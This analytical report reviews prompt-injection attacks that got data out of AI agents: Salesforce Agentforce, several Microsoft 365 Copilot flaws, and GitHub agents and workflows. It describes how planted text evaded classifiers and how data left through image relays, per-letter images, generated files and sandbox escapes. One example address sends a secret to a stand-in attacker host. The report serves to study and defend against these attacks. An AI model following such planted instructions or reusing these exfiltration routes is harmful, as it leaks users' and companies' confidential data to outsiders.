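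Noma called its attack ForcedLeak. According to the company's report, reposted under that name by the forum user Nytro (2025), the researchers first asked Agentforce what colour red and yellow make. It answered "Orange", which showed that the agent would take on requests unrelated to sales. They then looked for a form field that could hold their instructions. The name, company and email fields held at most 80 characters, but the description field held 42,000.

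The researchers filled that field with a short list of questions, some harmless and one asking for the email addresses of the company's other leads. The last item was an instruction to end the answer with an image whose web address contained those email addresses. The researchers then posed as an employee and asked Agentforce to check the new lead, answer its questions and draft an email with the results. The agent looked up the email addresses and produced the image link, and the request for the image sent them to Noma's server. EchoLeak, the Copilot flaw disclosed three months earlier, also used an image to send data out.

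Salesforce's defence against this was a content security policy, a list that tells the browser which domains a page may load images from. A stranger's server would not normally be on the list, but it still included a domain that Salesforce had allowed to expire. The domain was for sale for as little as $5, The Hacker News (2025) reported, and Noma bought it. Noma said the data could not have left without a way around the policy.

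The public form made the attacker's job easier than it was in Slack. The attacker didn't need an account, only a company that used the form and had an agent process the results. The attacker could also expect a sales team to look at new leads, but in Slack had to guess what a colleague would ask. The data was a list of customers' email addresses rather than the single key in the Slack attack.

ForcedLeak also removed the need for the victim to click, but it does not quite fit the definition of a zero-click attack because the employee had to ask the agent to deal with the attacker's submission. Noma's wording of that request also helped the attack, since telling an agent to respond to a lead's questions is practically telling it to obey the text in the form. A request for a one-line summary might have worked less well, but Noma gave no success rates for different requests.

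### Salesforce's fix and a second route out

Noma reported the flaw on 28 July 2025, and Salesforce acknowledged it three days later. Security Affairs' *ForcedLeak flaw in Salesforce Agentforce exposes CRM data via Prompt Injection* reported that Salesforce began enforcing a list of trusted web addresses for Agentforce's output on 8 September. Noma disclosed the flaw publicly on 25 September. SecurityWeek's *Salesforce AI Hack Enabled CRM Data Theft* reported that Salesforce also took back the expired domain.

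Between the report and the disclosure, Salesforce made another change because of prompt injection. Its *Security Advisories* for August 2025 announced that Agentforce would ask a person to confirm certain actions, such as resetting a password or updating a customer's contact details. The advisories do not mention ForcedLeak, and these confirmations would probably not have stopped it. A browser loads images to display an answer, so the employee would have had no action to approve.

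ForcedLeak was also attacker-initiated and demonstrated. The person who filled in the form chose which data to take and where to send it, while the employee only wanted to answer a sales enquiry. Noma ran the attack in its own test. The flaw scored 9.4 for severity. Salesforce said less than Slack had about whether anyone had exploited the flaw. Its statement in Infosecurity Magazine's *Critical Vulnerability in Salesforce AgentForce Exposed* covers the patches but does not mention whether anyone had taken customer data. Noma sensibly advised companies to search their existing leads for suspicious submissions, because planted text could sit in the database until an employee asked about it.

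Trusted web addresses blocked only one way to leak data. In April 2026, Security Boulevard's *Microsoft and Salesforce Patch AI Agent Flaws That Could Leak Sensitive Data* (2026) described another attack on Agentforce through a public lead form, in which the agent sent the CRM data by email. Capsule Security had found that flaw and a similar one in Microsoft's Copilot Studio, a tool for building agents. The summary in OECD's *Prompt Injection Attacks Lead to Data Leaks* (2026) describes vulnerabilities that Capsule discovered, although the title suggests that attackers had used them. Salesforce and Microsoft patched both flaws.

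## How could an email make Microsoft 365 Copilot send out company data?

In January 2025, researchers at the security firm Aim Security showed that a single email could make Microsoft 365 Copilot send an employee's confidential data to an outsider. The vulnerability, called EchoLeak, is listed as CVE-2025-32711 in the public catalogue of software flaws. The attack on Slack AI required an account in the victim's workspace, and the one on Agentforce required a company with a public web form, whereas almost every office worker has an email address that strangers can write to.

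Adir Gruss, a co-founder of Aim, told Fortune (2025) that the team spent about three months figuring out how Copilot worked internally. The attack had to get past each of Microsoft's several defences. Ravia (2025) gives the finders' own account in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*. Reddy and Gujral (2025) later analysed why each defence failed in *EchoLeak*.

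### Past the classifier and into the answer

Microsoft uses a classifier to screen the text that Copilot retrieves. The classifier is a program trained to recognise prompt injections, which Microsoft calls cross-prompt injection attacks (XPIA), and keep them from the model. It would probably have caught an email that ordered Copilot to ignore its instructions and send data to a web address.

Aim worded its email as an ordinary business request to the human recipient and never mentioned Copilot or AI. Offices receive similar requests every day, so a classifier strict enough to block it would also block a lot of legitimate mail. Ravia adds that good collections of real injections are scarce, and Microsoft would need them to train a better classifier.

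An email that passes the classifier does nothing until Copilot retrieves it. Many retrieval systems turn each passage of text into a list of numbers representing its meaning, then look for passages whose numbers are close to those of the question. In such a system, a short email on one subject comes up only when somebody asks about that subject. Aim didn't know exactly how Copilot's search worked, but guessed that it worked this way.

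The researchers therefore wrote one very long email with many sections. Each section was titled as a guide to a common office subject, such as leave of absence or onboarding, and contained the same instructions. Retrieval systems usually split long texts into pieces, so each section could match a question separately. If an employee asked how to apply for parental leave, Copilot might retrieve the section on leave. In Aim's test, Copilot retrieved the email for questions on various topics, though Ravia gives no success rate.

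The model then received the retrieved section along with the employee's question, the earlier messages in the conversation and any internal documents that the search had found. The section contained instructions to provide the most sensitive item in all that text. Aim calls this an "LLM scope violation", meaning that text from outside the organisation directs the model to data inside it.

The attacker didn't need to know what secrets the company had, because the model would pick one. If the employee had asked about the price of a planned takeover earlier in the conversation, the model might pick that price. The attacker still initiated the leak, since the planted instructions determined what kind of data to take and where to send it. The attack could reach only the model's input at that moment, which is much less than the employee's mailbox but could include the full conversation and several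 confidential files.

### Past the filters and out

Aim's first idea for getting the data out was a link with the secret in its address, as in the Slack attack. Copilot removed links to outside websites from its answers before the user could see them. But Markdown, the notation the model uses for formatting, allows a link's address either directly after its text or further down with a label, like a footnote. Microsoft's filter recognised only the first format. Willison gave Microsoft credit for restricting links at all, and thought it had forgotten the lesser-known format.

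A user would still have had to click a link, so the researchers switched to an image, which a browser loads automatically. The footnote format worked for images too. But Copilot's content security policy only allowed images from a list of permitted sources, as Salesforce's did. Most of the domains on Microsoft's list belonged to Microsoft.

Aim searched this list for a service that would fetch an outside page on request. SharePoint, which companies use for internal websites and shared files, offered one, but the victim would first have had to accept an invitation to the attacker's site. Microsoft Teams, the company's chat and meeting program, offered another that needed no invitation. With invented names, the image's address would look something like this:

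`relay.example/fetch?page=attacker.example/TAKEOVER-PRICE-40M`

The browser sends this request to the relay, which is on the list. The relay then opens the page whose address follows the question mark, and the attacker's server logs that address, which includes the price. The policy worked as designed, but it controls only what the browser contacts, not what Microsoft's servers contact afterwards. Security engineers call this technique server-side request forgery.

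Copilot normally cites its sources, which might have led a suspicious employee to the email. But the email asked its "recipient" never to refer to it, for compliance reasons, and Copilot left it out of the citations. According to Reddy and Gujral, the employee would have noticed at most what looked like a broken link or image.

### What the victim still had to do

EchoLeak was zero-click, and the employee never had to open the email, but they did have to use Copilot. Fortune describes Copilot as scanning emails in the background and acting on the hidden instructions, which suggests that the theft could begin as soon as the email arrived. Reddy and Gujral instead assume a victim who at least occasionally asks Copilot something, such as to summarise recent emails. Their assumption fits Aim's method better, since there would be little reason to write a section for every common office question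 if Copilot acted on new mail by itself.

Employees who never used Copilot were therefore safe from this attack, but each use gave the attacker another chance. Avoiding Copilot is hardly a practical defence, because companies pay for it so that people will use it. Warning employees about suspicious emails wouldn't have helped either. Ravia says that, to Aim's knowledge, no user behaviour or administrator's setting could have prevented the attack.

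### Five months to a fix

Aim reported EchoLeak to Microsoft in January 2025. Kundu reports in *Microsoft fixes first known zero-click attack on an AI agent* that Microsoft had a first fix ready by April, but its engineers found further flaws in May. The company had first tried to block the attack's pathways in each affected program, but failed. It finished the repair on its own servers in May, so customers had nothing to install. Microsoft and Aim made the flaw public on 11 June. Gruss thought five months was a long time for a flaw of this kind.

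EchoLeak had a severity score of 9.3, but Microsoft said it had found no evidence that anyone had exploited the flaw. It was a real flaw in a real product, but the only documented attacks are the researchers' own. Some descriptions make it sound more like a theft than it was. Reddy and Gujral's title calls it a "real-world" exploit, and their introduction describes it as the first known case of somebody weaponising prompt injection to steal data from a production system.

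Microsoft's fixes reportedly included removing footnote-style links and embedded images from incoming outside content, and adding options to keep outside messages away from Copilot in some situations. Using these options makes Copilot less useful. For example, a manager can't use it to look up the delivery date a supplier promised if it can't read the supplier's email.

### Three sequels in 2026

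Researchers got data out of Copilot in 2026 with attacks they named SearchLeak, ChatMate and ReLeak. The researchers included Aim's team, which by then belonged to another company.

| Attack | Where the instructions were | What the user did | How the data got out | Microsoft's fix |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak | Outside email | Asked Copilot an ordinary question | Image request through Teams | May 2025 |
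| SearchLeak | Link to Copilot's search page | Clicked the link | Image request through Bing | June 2026 |
| ChatMate | Hidden text in a document | Uploaded the document to Copilot | Server underneath the code sandbox | March and April 2026 |
| ReLeak, images | Outside email | Made an ordinary request | Image request through Bing | 15 November 2026 |
| ReLeak, files | Outside email | Made an ordinary request | Link in a generated file, opened by a Microsoft service | 11 November 2026 |
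| ReLeak, code | Outside email | Made an ordinary request | Direct connection from the code sandbox | 17 September 2026 |

### SearchLeak: a question written by somebody else

Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) describes an attack on the search page of Copilot's enterprise version. Like many search pages, this one accepted a query in its web address so that people could link to a search. But Copilot treated the query as a prompt and ran it as soon as the page opened. An attacker who got an employee to click a link could therefore choose the prompt that Copilot ran for that employee.

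In the demonstration, the question contained instructions for Copilot to find an email, copy its subject line and put the text into the address of an image. Services often put login codes in subject lines, and a thief who already had the victim's password could use such a code to get into another account. Varonis, which sells data security software, says the same method could reach calendars and company files that the victim had permission to open.

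Microsoft tried to block images in these answers by converting each finished answer to plain text, so that the browser would not load anything. But Copilot shows an answer bit by bit while the model is still writing it, so the browser had already requested the image before the conversion happened. Programmers call this a race condition, because the result depends on which of two events happens first.

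The content security policy still blocked images from unapproved sources, but it allowed images from Bing, Microsoft's search engine. Bing's image search would fetch a picture from any address a user supplied, so the browser contacted Bing, which then contacted the attacker's server. The link led to a real Microsoft address, so there was no obvious reason for a filter that checks links for suspicious websites to block it.

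Microsoft fixed SearchLeak in June 2026, and customers again didn't need to do anything, according to SC Media's *SearchLeak vulnerability allows data theft from Microsoft 365 Copilot Enterprise*. Reports of its severity differ widely. Expert Insights' *Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Let One Click Exfiltrate Emails, MFA Codes* (2026) explains that Microsoft scored it 6.5, or medium, because the victim had to click. The US National Vulnerability Database scored it 7.5, or high, because it assumed no user action was needed. Varonis calls it critical and says Microsoft gave it a "max severity rating of critical". TechRadar reported a rating of "10/10 critical".

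Microsoft gives flaws both a severity rating and a numerical score, so "critical" and 6.5 can both be right. TechRadar's 10 probably comes from reading "max severity" as the highest possible score. Microsoft's 6.5 fits the published attack better than TechRadar's 10 because Varonis describes an attack that needs a click.

### ChatMate: a conversation with a stranger

The code interpreter lets Copilot write and run small programs, for instance to make a chart from a spreadsheet. The programs run in a sandbox, a closed environment that should have no internet connection. Ori Lahav of Rubrik Zero Labs, the research group of another data security company, found a way out of it.

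The attack began with a Word document containing text hidden from the user. When an employee uploaded the document and asked for help with it, the text made Copilot run the attacker's code. According to the summary in *Phantom Keystrokes* (Fiehler, 2026), the code got past Copilot's safety checks, took full control of the sandbox and then used a flaw in Microsoft's cloud software to reach the server underneath. That server was connected to the internet.

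EchoLeak's instructions were fixed when the attacker sent the email. ChatMate opened a two-way channel, so an attacker could type a request into the victim's Copilot session, read the answer and choose the next request. For example, an attacker who saw a merger mentioned in one answer could then ask for the contract. All the requests ran with the victim's permissions. Rubrik calls this technique "remote prompt execution".

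ChatMate involved no link, but the employee had to handle the attacker's document, so neither "one-click" nor "zero-click" describes it. The document could look like the routine business documents people often upload to Copilot.

Rubrik Zero Labs' *Breaking the M365 Copilot Sandbox with ChatMate* (2026) also reports that Lahav could not reach other customers' data from the server. Microsoft had fixed the flaws before Lahav recorded the demonstration, so the video simulates the internet connection to the attacker, but the rest is real. Fiehler describes the attack as "relatively easy to do". That might have been true of using the finished attack, but the technical report shows that finding it was hard. Lahav needed five separate flaws in Microsoft's cloud products and at one point gave up for about a month.

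Lahav reported the flaws on 10 February 2026. Microsoft fixed the one inside the sandbox on 19 March and the escape to the server in mid-April. It rated the escape 8.8 for severity and paid a $48,000 reward. The escape also affected other Microsoft cloud products because the faulty software was not specific to Copilot, which made ChatMate as much a conventional hacking discovery as an AI one.

### ReLeak: one email and three exits

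Cato Networks bought Aim Security in September 2025, and Aim's researchers became Cato AI Labs. On 3 December 2026, the team's *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026) reported three new zero-click ways to take data out of Copilot. According to Infosecurity Magazine, AI agents helped the researchers this time by generating and testing malicious prompts.

The attack again started with an outside email that the victim never had to open. Copilot refused when the email contained a direct order. TechRadar's *Hackers build zero-click attacks in Microsoft Copilot* reports that Copilot complied when the same demand was worded as a routine business requirement for finishing the user's task. Microsoft's injection classifier failed to stop this version.

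The first method sent out the stolen data in the address of an image, with Bing as the relay. Infosecurity Magazine and Punto Informatico's *ReLeak* both name Bing, but TechRadar names Teams, which was the relay in EchoLeak.

For the second, Copilot created a file containing a link with the data in its address. The researchers made this work with Word, Excel, PowerPoint and PDF files. Copilot saved the file to the company's online storage, where a Microsoft background service processed it and opened the link. The content security policy didn't prevent this, since no browser had to load anything. Closing the chat didn't prevent it either, because the background service could open the link later.

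The third way to send data out was directly from the code interpreter's sandbox, although Microsoft's documentation said the sandbox blocked outgoing traffic. According to TechRadar, settings inside the sandbox directed programs to an intermediary, and Copilot could connect to the internet directly once the researchers had it remove those settings.

This last finding seems to conflict with ChatMate. Early in 2026, Lahav tried to reach the internet from inside the sandbox, found every attempt blocked, and so broke into the server underneath. A few months later, Cato reached the internet without leaving the sandbox. Microsoft may have changed the sandbox in the meantime, or Lahav may have missed a route that already existed.

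Cato reported the three flaws between 29 July and 20 August, and Microsoft had fixed them all by 15 November. The sandbox flaw, CVE-2026-78501, has a severity score of 8.6. When Cato published, the other two had reserved CVE numbers but no public details, so outsiders could not compare their scores. An attacker could in principle use all three flaws together, so that the attack would still succeed if one failed, but Cato did not demonstrate this.

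### Did Microsoft repair the exits and leave the cause?

Cato's researchers say that "too little progress has been made" since EchoLeak. They think Microsoft has improved its defences, but Copilot can still follow instructions hidden in an attacker's text. In their view, each new ability Copilot gains also adds another way for data to leak. Cato sells protection for AI systems, so it benefits from this conclusion, but its evidence is fairly good because Microsoft accepted and patched all the flaws.

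The disguised instructions are the most direct support for the charge. In January 2025 Aim got past the classifier by wording its instructions as a business request to a person. In the summer of 2026 the same team succeeded with instructions worded as a business requirement. The team may have had to change its wording, and Copilot's refusal of the direct order shows that some protection was working. But crude commands also worked poorly against Copilot in 2025, so the refusal is not much of an advance.

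SearchLeak used a prompt planted in a link. Varonis had already used this method against the personal version of Copilot, in an attack it called Reprompt, and was surprised that it worked on the enterprise version too. In December 2025, Varonis told Microsoft about another attack of this type, CoSnitch, which TechRadar's *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot by continually asking it questions* describes. CoSnitch could also plant instructions in Copilot's long-term memory through a web page that the user asked Copilot to summarise. Those instructions would remain after the user changed their password.

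The charge may even understate the problem with the routes by which data can leave. Ravia's article on EchoLeak listed every domain from which Copilot could load images, including bing.com. Microsoft closed the route through Teams, but a year later Varonis got data out through Bing. Varonis then advised companies to check their lists of allowed domains for any service that fetches outside addresses on request. Within about two months, Cato reported its own route through Bing, which may have used a different feature but relied on the same weakness. Microsoft seems to have closed particular routes without removing the general one, a trusted service that will contact any server on request.

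After EchoLeak, Microsoft said that it had fully mitigated the issue and that customers didn't need to do anything. That claim covers only one flaw, and the later attacks don't contradict it because none of them reused the whole EchoLeak chain. Microsoft has also made some changes to how it screens input, such as the filtering of incoming mail that Reddy and Gujral mention. Neither Infosecurity Magazine nor TechRadar quotes a reply from Microsoft to the broader charge. Meanwhile, more injection flaws have appeared in official records, including one from May 2026 with a severity score of 7.5, listed in INCIBE's *CVE-2026-26164* (2026).

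David C doubts that Microsoft or anyone else can remove the cause. Reddy and Gujral propose marking outside text with special tags and telling the model never to obey it. This might help, but in Ye and colleagues' experiments the style of a text influenced models more than its tags did, so Copilot might still obey an email that reads like a well-written business request.

A more promising approach is to use safeguards that don't depend on the model's judgment. Reddy and Gujral also recommend access controls based on where text came from, and Gruss has called for a fundamental redesign of agents. Ordinary software could detect when an outside email enters the model's input, then switch off external images, links in generated files and network access for code until the conversation ends. The manager could still ask Copilot about the supplier's delivery date and compare it with an internal contract.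 The main loss would be that Copilot couldn't fetch things from the web in the same conversation.

Such a rule would have blocked EchoLeak and all three ReLeak exits if Microsoft had enforced it everywhere. It would not have stopped SearchLeak, because no outside email was involved and Copilot received the attacker's words as the user's own question. The remedy for SearchLeak is to make the user confirm a question that arrives in a link before Copilot runs it. No rule about the model's input can prevent an attack like ChatMate, which broke the software that enforces the limits.

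The charge is accurate, but it is a weaker criticism of Microsoft because no AI company can fully prevent prompt injection. It is fairer to criticize Microsoft over the routes by which data could leave Copilot, since it controls them completely and could have searched for other relays after the first one was found.

### No known victims

Nobody has documented a theft from a customer through EchoLeak, SearchLeak, ChatMate or ReLeak. Ravia writes that Microsoft confirmed no customers were affected by EchoLeak. Cato said it knew of no customers affected by ReLeak, and neither Varonis nor Rubrik reports any victims of the attack it described.

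Microsoft's statement is the strongest evidence because Copilot runs on its servers. Once the company knew how EchoLeak worked, it could search its records for Teams requests that led to unfamiliar servers with long strings of text in their addresses. It has not explained how it checked or how far back its records went, so outsiders can't judge how thorough the search was. A security firm's statement that it knows of no victims is much weaker evidence, because the firm can't see other companies' Copilot sessions.

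The lack of reports from customers is even weaker evidence. VentureBeat pointed out that another bug, which let Copilot read emails labelled confidential, operated entirely inside Microsoft's infrastructure, where customers' security tools could not observe it. The same is largely true of EchoLeak. A company monitoring its own network would have seen an employee's browser contact Microsoft, which is routine. The request to the attacker came from a Microsoft server, and the employee saw at most a broken image.

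There were probably few thefts, if any. Finding such an attack took specialists weeks or months, and a criminal with the same skills could often get into a mailbox more easily with a stolen password. Large-scale use would probably have left evidence, such as the same long email in thousands of mailboxes. But a single careful theft from one company would be far harder to rule out.

These attacks may leave traces in a company's own systems, which it could search if it wanted more than Microsoft's assurance. The EchoLeak email would stay in the mailbox unless somebody deleted it, and one of ReLeak's methods for sending data out left a generated file in the company's storage with the stolen data written into a link.

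## How could a public GitHub issue expose private code?

Researchers needed an image, a link or a gap in a sandbox to get data out of Copilot. Getting data out through a coding agent is often easier, because coding agents routinely publish text. Many of them work on GitHub, a website where programmers store code and discuss changes to it.

GitHub keeps each project in a repository, which can be public or private. On most public repositories, anyone with an account can open an issue, usually to report a bug or ask for a feature. They can also open a pull request, which proposes a change to the project's files and stays publicly visible even if the owner never accepts it. If an owner has both public and private repositories, connecting an agent to the account gives the agent access to private data, text written by strangers and a place to publish. Willison wrote in *GitHub MCP Exploited* that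 this single connection combines all three elements of what he calls the lethal trifecta.

### Fan mail for a Pac-Man game

In May 2025, Marco Milanta and Luca Beurer-Kellner of the security firm Invariant Labs showed how a stranger could use a public GitHub issue to expose private code. Their report, *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025), describes a test account with a public repository, which held a simple Pac-Man game, and several private repositories, which held personal projects. The account's owner used Claude 4 Opus in Claude Desktop, Anthropic's chatbot program for computers. The program connected to GitHub through GitHub's official MCP server, software that turns a model's tool calls into requests to the website.

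In the issue, the attacker praised the game, regretted that its author was not better known, and asked for a chapter about the author in the README, the file that introduces a project to visitors. The agent was to read the README of every repository the author had and use them to write the chapter. According to heise online's *Attack via GitHub MCP server*, the attacker also claimed that the author didn't care about privacy and asked for a list of all the author's other repositories.

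The leak began when the owner asked Claude to look at the open issues in the Pac-Man repository. Claude fetched the issues and found the stranger's request among them. It then read the private repositories using the owner's access token, a key that lets a program act on somebody's account. It wrote the chapter and proposed it in a pull request on the Pac-Man repository. The chapter included the names of private projects, the owner's salary and the owner's plan to move to South America.

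The owner could still have rejected the pull request, but anyone could already read it. An attacker initiated this leak, because the stranger chose both what to collect and where to put it. Researchers demonstrated the leak using a test account and test secrets.

### Sound code and approved tools

The MCP server worked as its programmers intended each time Claude called it. It returned the issues of a public repository, then returned files that the token's holder was entitled to read, and then opened a pull request that the same person was entitled to open. The harm came from the order of these calls, and the server had no information about why Claude made them. A request for a private README looks the same whether the owner wanted the file or a stranger's issue prompted the request.

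Invariant Labs calls such a sequence a "toxic agent flow" and concluded that GitHub could not fix it by patching the server. Heise online also found no bug in the server. It criticized the Model Context Protocol for neglecting security, for example by putting session identifiers in web addresses, but the attack used none of those weaknesses.

Earlier attacks on MCP had relied on tampered tools. Here the tools came from GitHub and the owner had connected them on purpose, so vetting them before installation would not have stopped the attack.

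As a safeguard, Claude Desktop asks the user by default to confirm each tool call. But Invariant Labs says that many users choose "Always Allow" and stop watching what the agent does, though it gives no figure. Even a careful user would have struggled to spot the attack, because reading a README looks harmless and the user may have to approve several such steps before anything is obviously wrong. The last request, to open a pull request, would have revealed the attack only to someone who read the proposed text. Few testers in Anthropic's later study refused even a clearly dangerous command, so most people probably wouldn't catch a paragraph about the author.

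Invariant Labs chose Claude 4 Opus partly to show that a new model with thorough safety training could still be compromised by a fairly simple prompt injection. It reports that many ready-made injection detectors missed the attack. The company recommends software that monitors and restricts agents, which it also sells. Still, its demonstration is easy to check because it published the issue, the pull request and the full record of the agent's steps.

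### One picture for each letter

The next attack could work without the agent publishing anything. In June 2025 a researcher at Legit Security, another security company, found a flaw in GitHub Copilot Chat, an assistant on GitHub's website that answers questions about code. Legit Security's *CamoLeak* explains that anyone able to open a pull request could plant the instructions in a hidden comment in its description. GitHub supports hidden comments as an ordinary feature, and stores their text without displaying it. Copilot therefore received the whole description, including instructions that a person reading the page could not see.

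The victim was anyone who opened the page and asked Copilot to explain the pull request. Copilot worked with that person's permissions, which might give it access to private repositories the attacker could not open. The researcher first had Copilot put private code into a link, which the victim would have had to click, and then looked for a way to use images instead.

GitHub allowed the browser to load images only from GitHub's own domains, and it displayed outside images through a relay called Camo. Camo is stricter than the relays that let data out of Microsoft 365 Copilot, because it fetches an image only if the address carries a signature that GitHub generated beforehand. An attacker can't add a stolen password to a signed address without invalidating the signature, and can't get an address containing the password signed in advance without already knowing the password.

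The researcher got around this by having GitHub sign one address for every letter and symbol. The hidden comment contained the whole set, with instructions for Copilot to play a "small game" of spelling out private text in pictures. For the word KEY, the browser would request the picture for K, then E, then Y, and the attacker's server would log the requests in that order. Every picture was a single transparent dot, so the victim saw nothing. A random number at the end of each address kept the browser from reusing a stored picture when a letter came up twice. Ayush Paul's attack on Claude used much the same idea, with a link for every letter.

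The researcher used this method to extract the description of an unpatched security flaw from a private project, and to have Copilot search a victim's code for Amazon cloud keys. Legit Security gives the Copilot flaw a severity score of 9.6. GitHub had fixed it by 14 August, disabling all images in Copilot Chat. This was broader than closing one relay at a time and probably wiser, since the chat can work without images. But hidden text can still influence an answer, and the researcher had also used it to make Copilot recommend a malicious software package, which requires no image.

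The OECD's *GitHub Copilot Chat Vulnerability Exposes Private Code and Secrets*, an AI-generated entry in its monitor, classifies the case as an incident with realised harm because the tests extracted data. But the private repository shown in the write-up belonged to Legit Security, so this report counts the case as a demonstrated leak, regardless of how serious the flaw was.

### Agents that a stranger can start

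The owner of the Pac-Man game and the user of Copilot Chat both had to ask a question before anything could go wrong. Build pipelines often remove that step. A build pipeline is a set of automated tasks, such as testing new code, that a project runs whenever something changes. GitHub's version is called GitHub Actions, and by 2026 projects were using it to run agents that reviewed code or sorted issues. According to *GitInject* (2026), a paper on attacks against such agents, they typically have a token for the repository, permission to post comments and the ability to run commands on the machine. If an agent is set to run on every new issue, anyone who files an issue starts it.

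In *Comment And Control*, Guan (2026) used this method to take passwords and keys from the machine itself, and it worked on agents from three companies. A stolen repository token may in turn give access to private code. SecurityWeek's *Claude Code, Gemini CLI, GitHub Copilot Agents Vulnerable to Prompt Injection* reports that security engineer Aonan Guan discovered the method with help from Zhengyu Liu and Gavin Zhong of Johns Hopkins University.

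Anthropic's Claude Code Security Review checks pull requests for security flaws. It copied each pull request's title straight into the model's prompt. Guan wrote a title with instructions to inspect the programs running on the machine, whose settings included Anthropic's API key and a GitHub token. The agent then posted both in a public comment, as though they were a flaw in the code. Lyons (2026) points out in *Agents hooked into GitHub can steal creds* that the attacker could afterwards change the title to something dull like "fix typo", close the pull request and delete the agent's comment.

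Google's Gemini CLI Action uses an AI model to respond to GitHub issues. Researchers planted instructions in an issue's title and comments, including a fake "trusted content" section in which they told the model it could safely share keys. The model then posted its own API key as a public comment.

Stealing secrets from GitHub's Copilot Agent, which writes code to resolve issues, was harder. Somebody at the project had to assign the issue to the agent, and GitHub had added protections that did not depend on the model. The person who assigned the issue saw only a harmless request, because the instructions were in a hidden comment. GitHub removed secrets from the settings that the agent's commands received, but other programs on the machine still had secrets in their settings, and the agent could inspect those programs. A scanner searched outgoing changes for text that looked like a key, but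 it did not recognize the keys once the agent had encoded them. A firewall blocked connections to unfamiliar websites, but it had to allow GitHub so that the agent could submit code. The agent leaked the keys in a file attached to a pull request.

Not every project with such an agent was exposed. GitHub normally withholds secrets from automated workflows triggered by an outsider's pull request, though some projects override this. Guan's published tests used repositories set up for testing.

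### Bounties without warnings

Anthropic paid Guan's team a bug bounty of $100, Google paid $1,337 and GitHub paid $500. Lyons reports that none of the three companies published a security advisory or assigned a CVE number.

Anthropic rated the severity of its flaw 9.4 out of 10 and blocked the command Guan had used to list running programs. Guan replies that another common command gives the same information. Anthropic also stated that the tool "is not designed to be hardened against prompt injection", and now advises people in its documentation to use it only on pull requests they trust. It recommends a GitHub setting that holds back an outsider's pull request until someone who runs the project has looked at it. This would probably have worked against Guan's title, which was visible, but it is weaker against hidden comments.

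GitHub at first closed the report, calling the problem a known issue that it could not reproduce. Guan then used Copilot's code to show that GitHub had meant to keep those secrets from the agent. GitHub reopened the report, called the exposure a "previously identified architectural limitation" and paid in March 2026. It said it was looking for ways to restrict access further.

Guan told Lyons that some users had pinned their setup to an older, vulnerable version and might never learn of the danger. The companies did not answer Lyons's questions. Anthropic had changed its code in response to the report, so there was at least an update to announce. The companies might argue that a CVE entry does not suit this case, because it usually identifies a faulty version and a corrected one, and an agent that reads strangers' text may have no fully corrected version. But a warning in the documentation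 reaches people about to install a tool much more reliably than those who installed it months ago.

In August 2026, the security firm Novee presented flaws in coding agents from Anthropic, Google and OpenAI at the Black Hat security conference. *Black Hat 2026* (Underhill, 2026) reports that a single GitHub issue from an outsider could lead to stolen credentials, let the attacker run code, or compromise software that others depend on. Novee found the flaws in the AI companies' own repositories, where the agents ran with default settings, which makes it harder for companies to argue that customers had set up their agents carelessly.

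### GitLost and the word "Additionally"

Meanwhile, GitHub had launched its own agent product for build pipelines, Agentic Workflows, in February 2026. A team describes a task in plain language, and an agent running on Copilot or Claude carries it out. GitHub expected attacks, and its *Under the hood* (2026), published in March, assumes that the agent will try to read and write things it shouldn't and mentions public comments as a way for an agent to leak secrets.

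Its design therefore keeps keys away from the agent and prevents it from writing to GitHub directly. The agent can only propose a comment or a pull request. After it finishes, ordinary software checks its proposals against the types and number of actions the workflow permits, and removes secrets and unwanted content.

*GitLost* showed in July 2026 that a stranger could still use a public GitHub issue to extract a private file. Sasi Levi, who wrote it, works for Noma Security, the company that disclosed ForcedLeak. When somebody assigned an issue, the workflow in the test read its title and text and posted a comment in reply. The workflow could also read the organisation's other repositories, including private ones.

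Levi wrote the issue to look like a note from a vice president of sales after a customer meeting. Its requests included a question about the README of a private repository. An automatic rule assigned the issue, so no employee had to do anything. The agent fetched that README and one from a public repository, and posted both in a public comment.

Levi tried variations of the demand, as an attacker would, and found that the word "Additionally" got the model to answer when it would otherwise have refused. A reader quoted in InfoQ's *Indirect Prompt Injection Exploits GitHub's AI Agent to Leak Private Repository Data* (2026) suggests the word made the demand look like part of the current task. This is a guess, but it fits what Ye and colleagues found about disguised instructions.

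GitHub's checks on outgoing text probably didn't stop the leak because this workflow was supposed to post comments, and a README needn't contain a key or a suspicious link. The README was private only because of the repository it came from, and software that examines a comment's wording can't detect that.

The customer configured the agent unsafely, but GitHub made that easy to do without noticing. Expert Insights' *Researchers Trick Misconfigured GitHub AI Agent Into Leaking a Private Repo* (2026) calls the workflow misconfigured, whereas Noma calls GitLost a critical vulnerability. GitHub's *Cross-Repository Operations* partly supports the first description. By default, an agent can read only the current repository and public ones, so somebody has to supply an extra token before it can read other private repositories. But GitHub offers this as a normal feature. A separate setting limits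 which repositories the agent may read, and if the customer leaves it out, the agent can read everything the token gives access to.

In July, The Next Web's *‘GitLost’* reported that there was no code fix and that GitHub had not added the documentation warning Noma had proposed. Forkast later reported that GitHub had updated the documentation to describe the risky setup, but had issued no CVE number, advisory or public statement. *GitHub Prompt Injection Exposed Private Repos via Issues* (Cross, 2026) found no confirmed use of the technique by real attackers as of September.

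Strangers do plant such text, though. *GitLost Flaw Lets Attackers Trick GitHub AI Agent Into Leaking Private Repos* reports that the security company Forcepoint had found ten hidden prompts on real web pages by April 2026. An organisation worried about GitLost has one advantage over Microsoft 365 Copilot customers, because it can search for the stolen text, which would appear in a public comment under its own agent's name.

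### Three ways to limit the damage

Researchers and GitHub have proposed restricting an agent to one repository per session, giving it a narrower token, and controlling what it may do after it reads certain material. The verdicts below are inferences from how each attack worked, not test results.

| Attack | One repository per session | Token for the public repository only | No public output from an agent that reads private data |
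|---|---|---|---|
| GitHub MCP | Stops it | Stops it | Stops it |
| Copilot Chat | Stops theft from other repositories | Copilot used the victim's own permissions | Stops it if the rule covers images |
| Comment and Control | No effect | Limits what a stolen token opens | Stops it only if the rule covers keys on the machine |
| GitLost | Stops it | Stops it | Stops it |

Invariant Labs wrote a sample rule for the first proposal. Software between the agent and its tools compares each call with earlier ones and stops the agent if the repository or its owner has changed. With this rule, Claude could have read the stranger's issue in the Pac-Man case but not the private projects. The rule is easy to check and doesn't require anybody to recognise an attack.

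Invariant Labs says that the restriction preserves full functionality "within authorized boundaries", but much ordinary work crosses those boundaries. GitHub's documentation gives the example of checking a proposed change against a library of code in another repository. A team that does this daily would soon ask for an exception, and one that covers both a public and a private repository would bring back the original danger.

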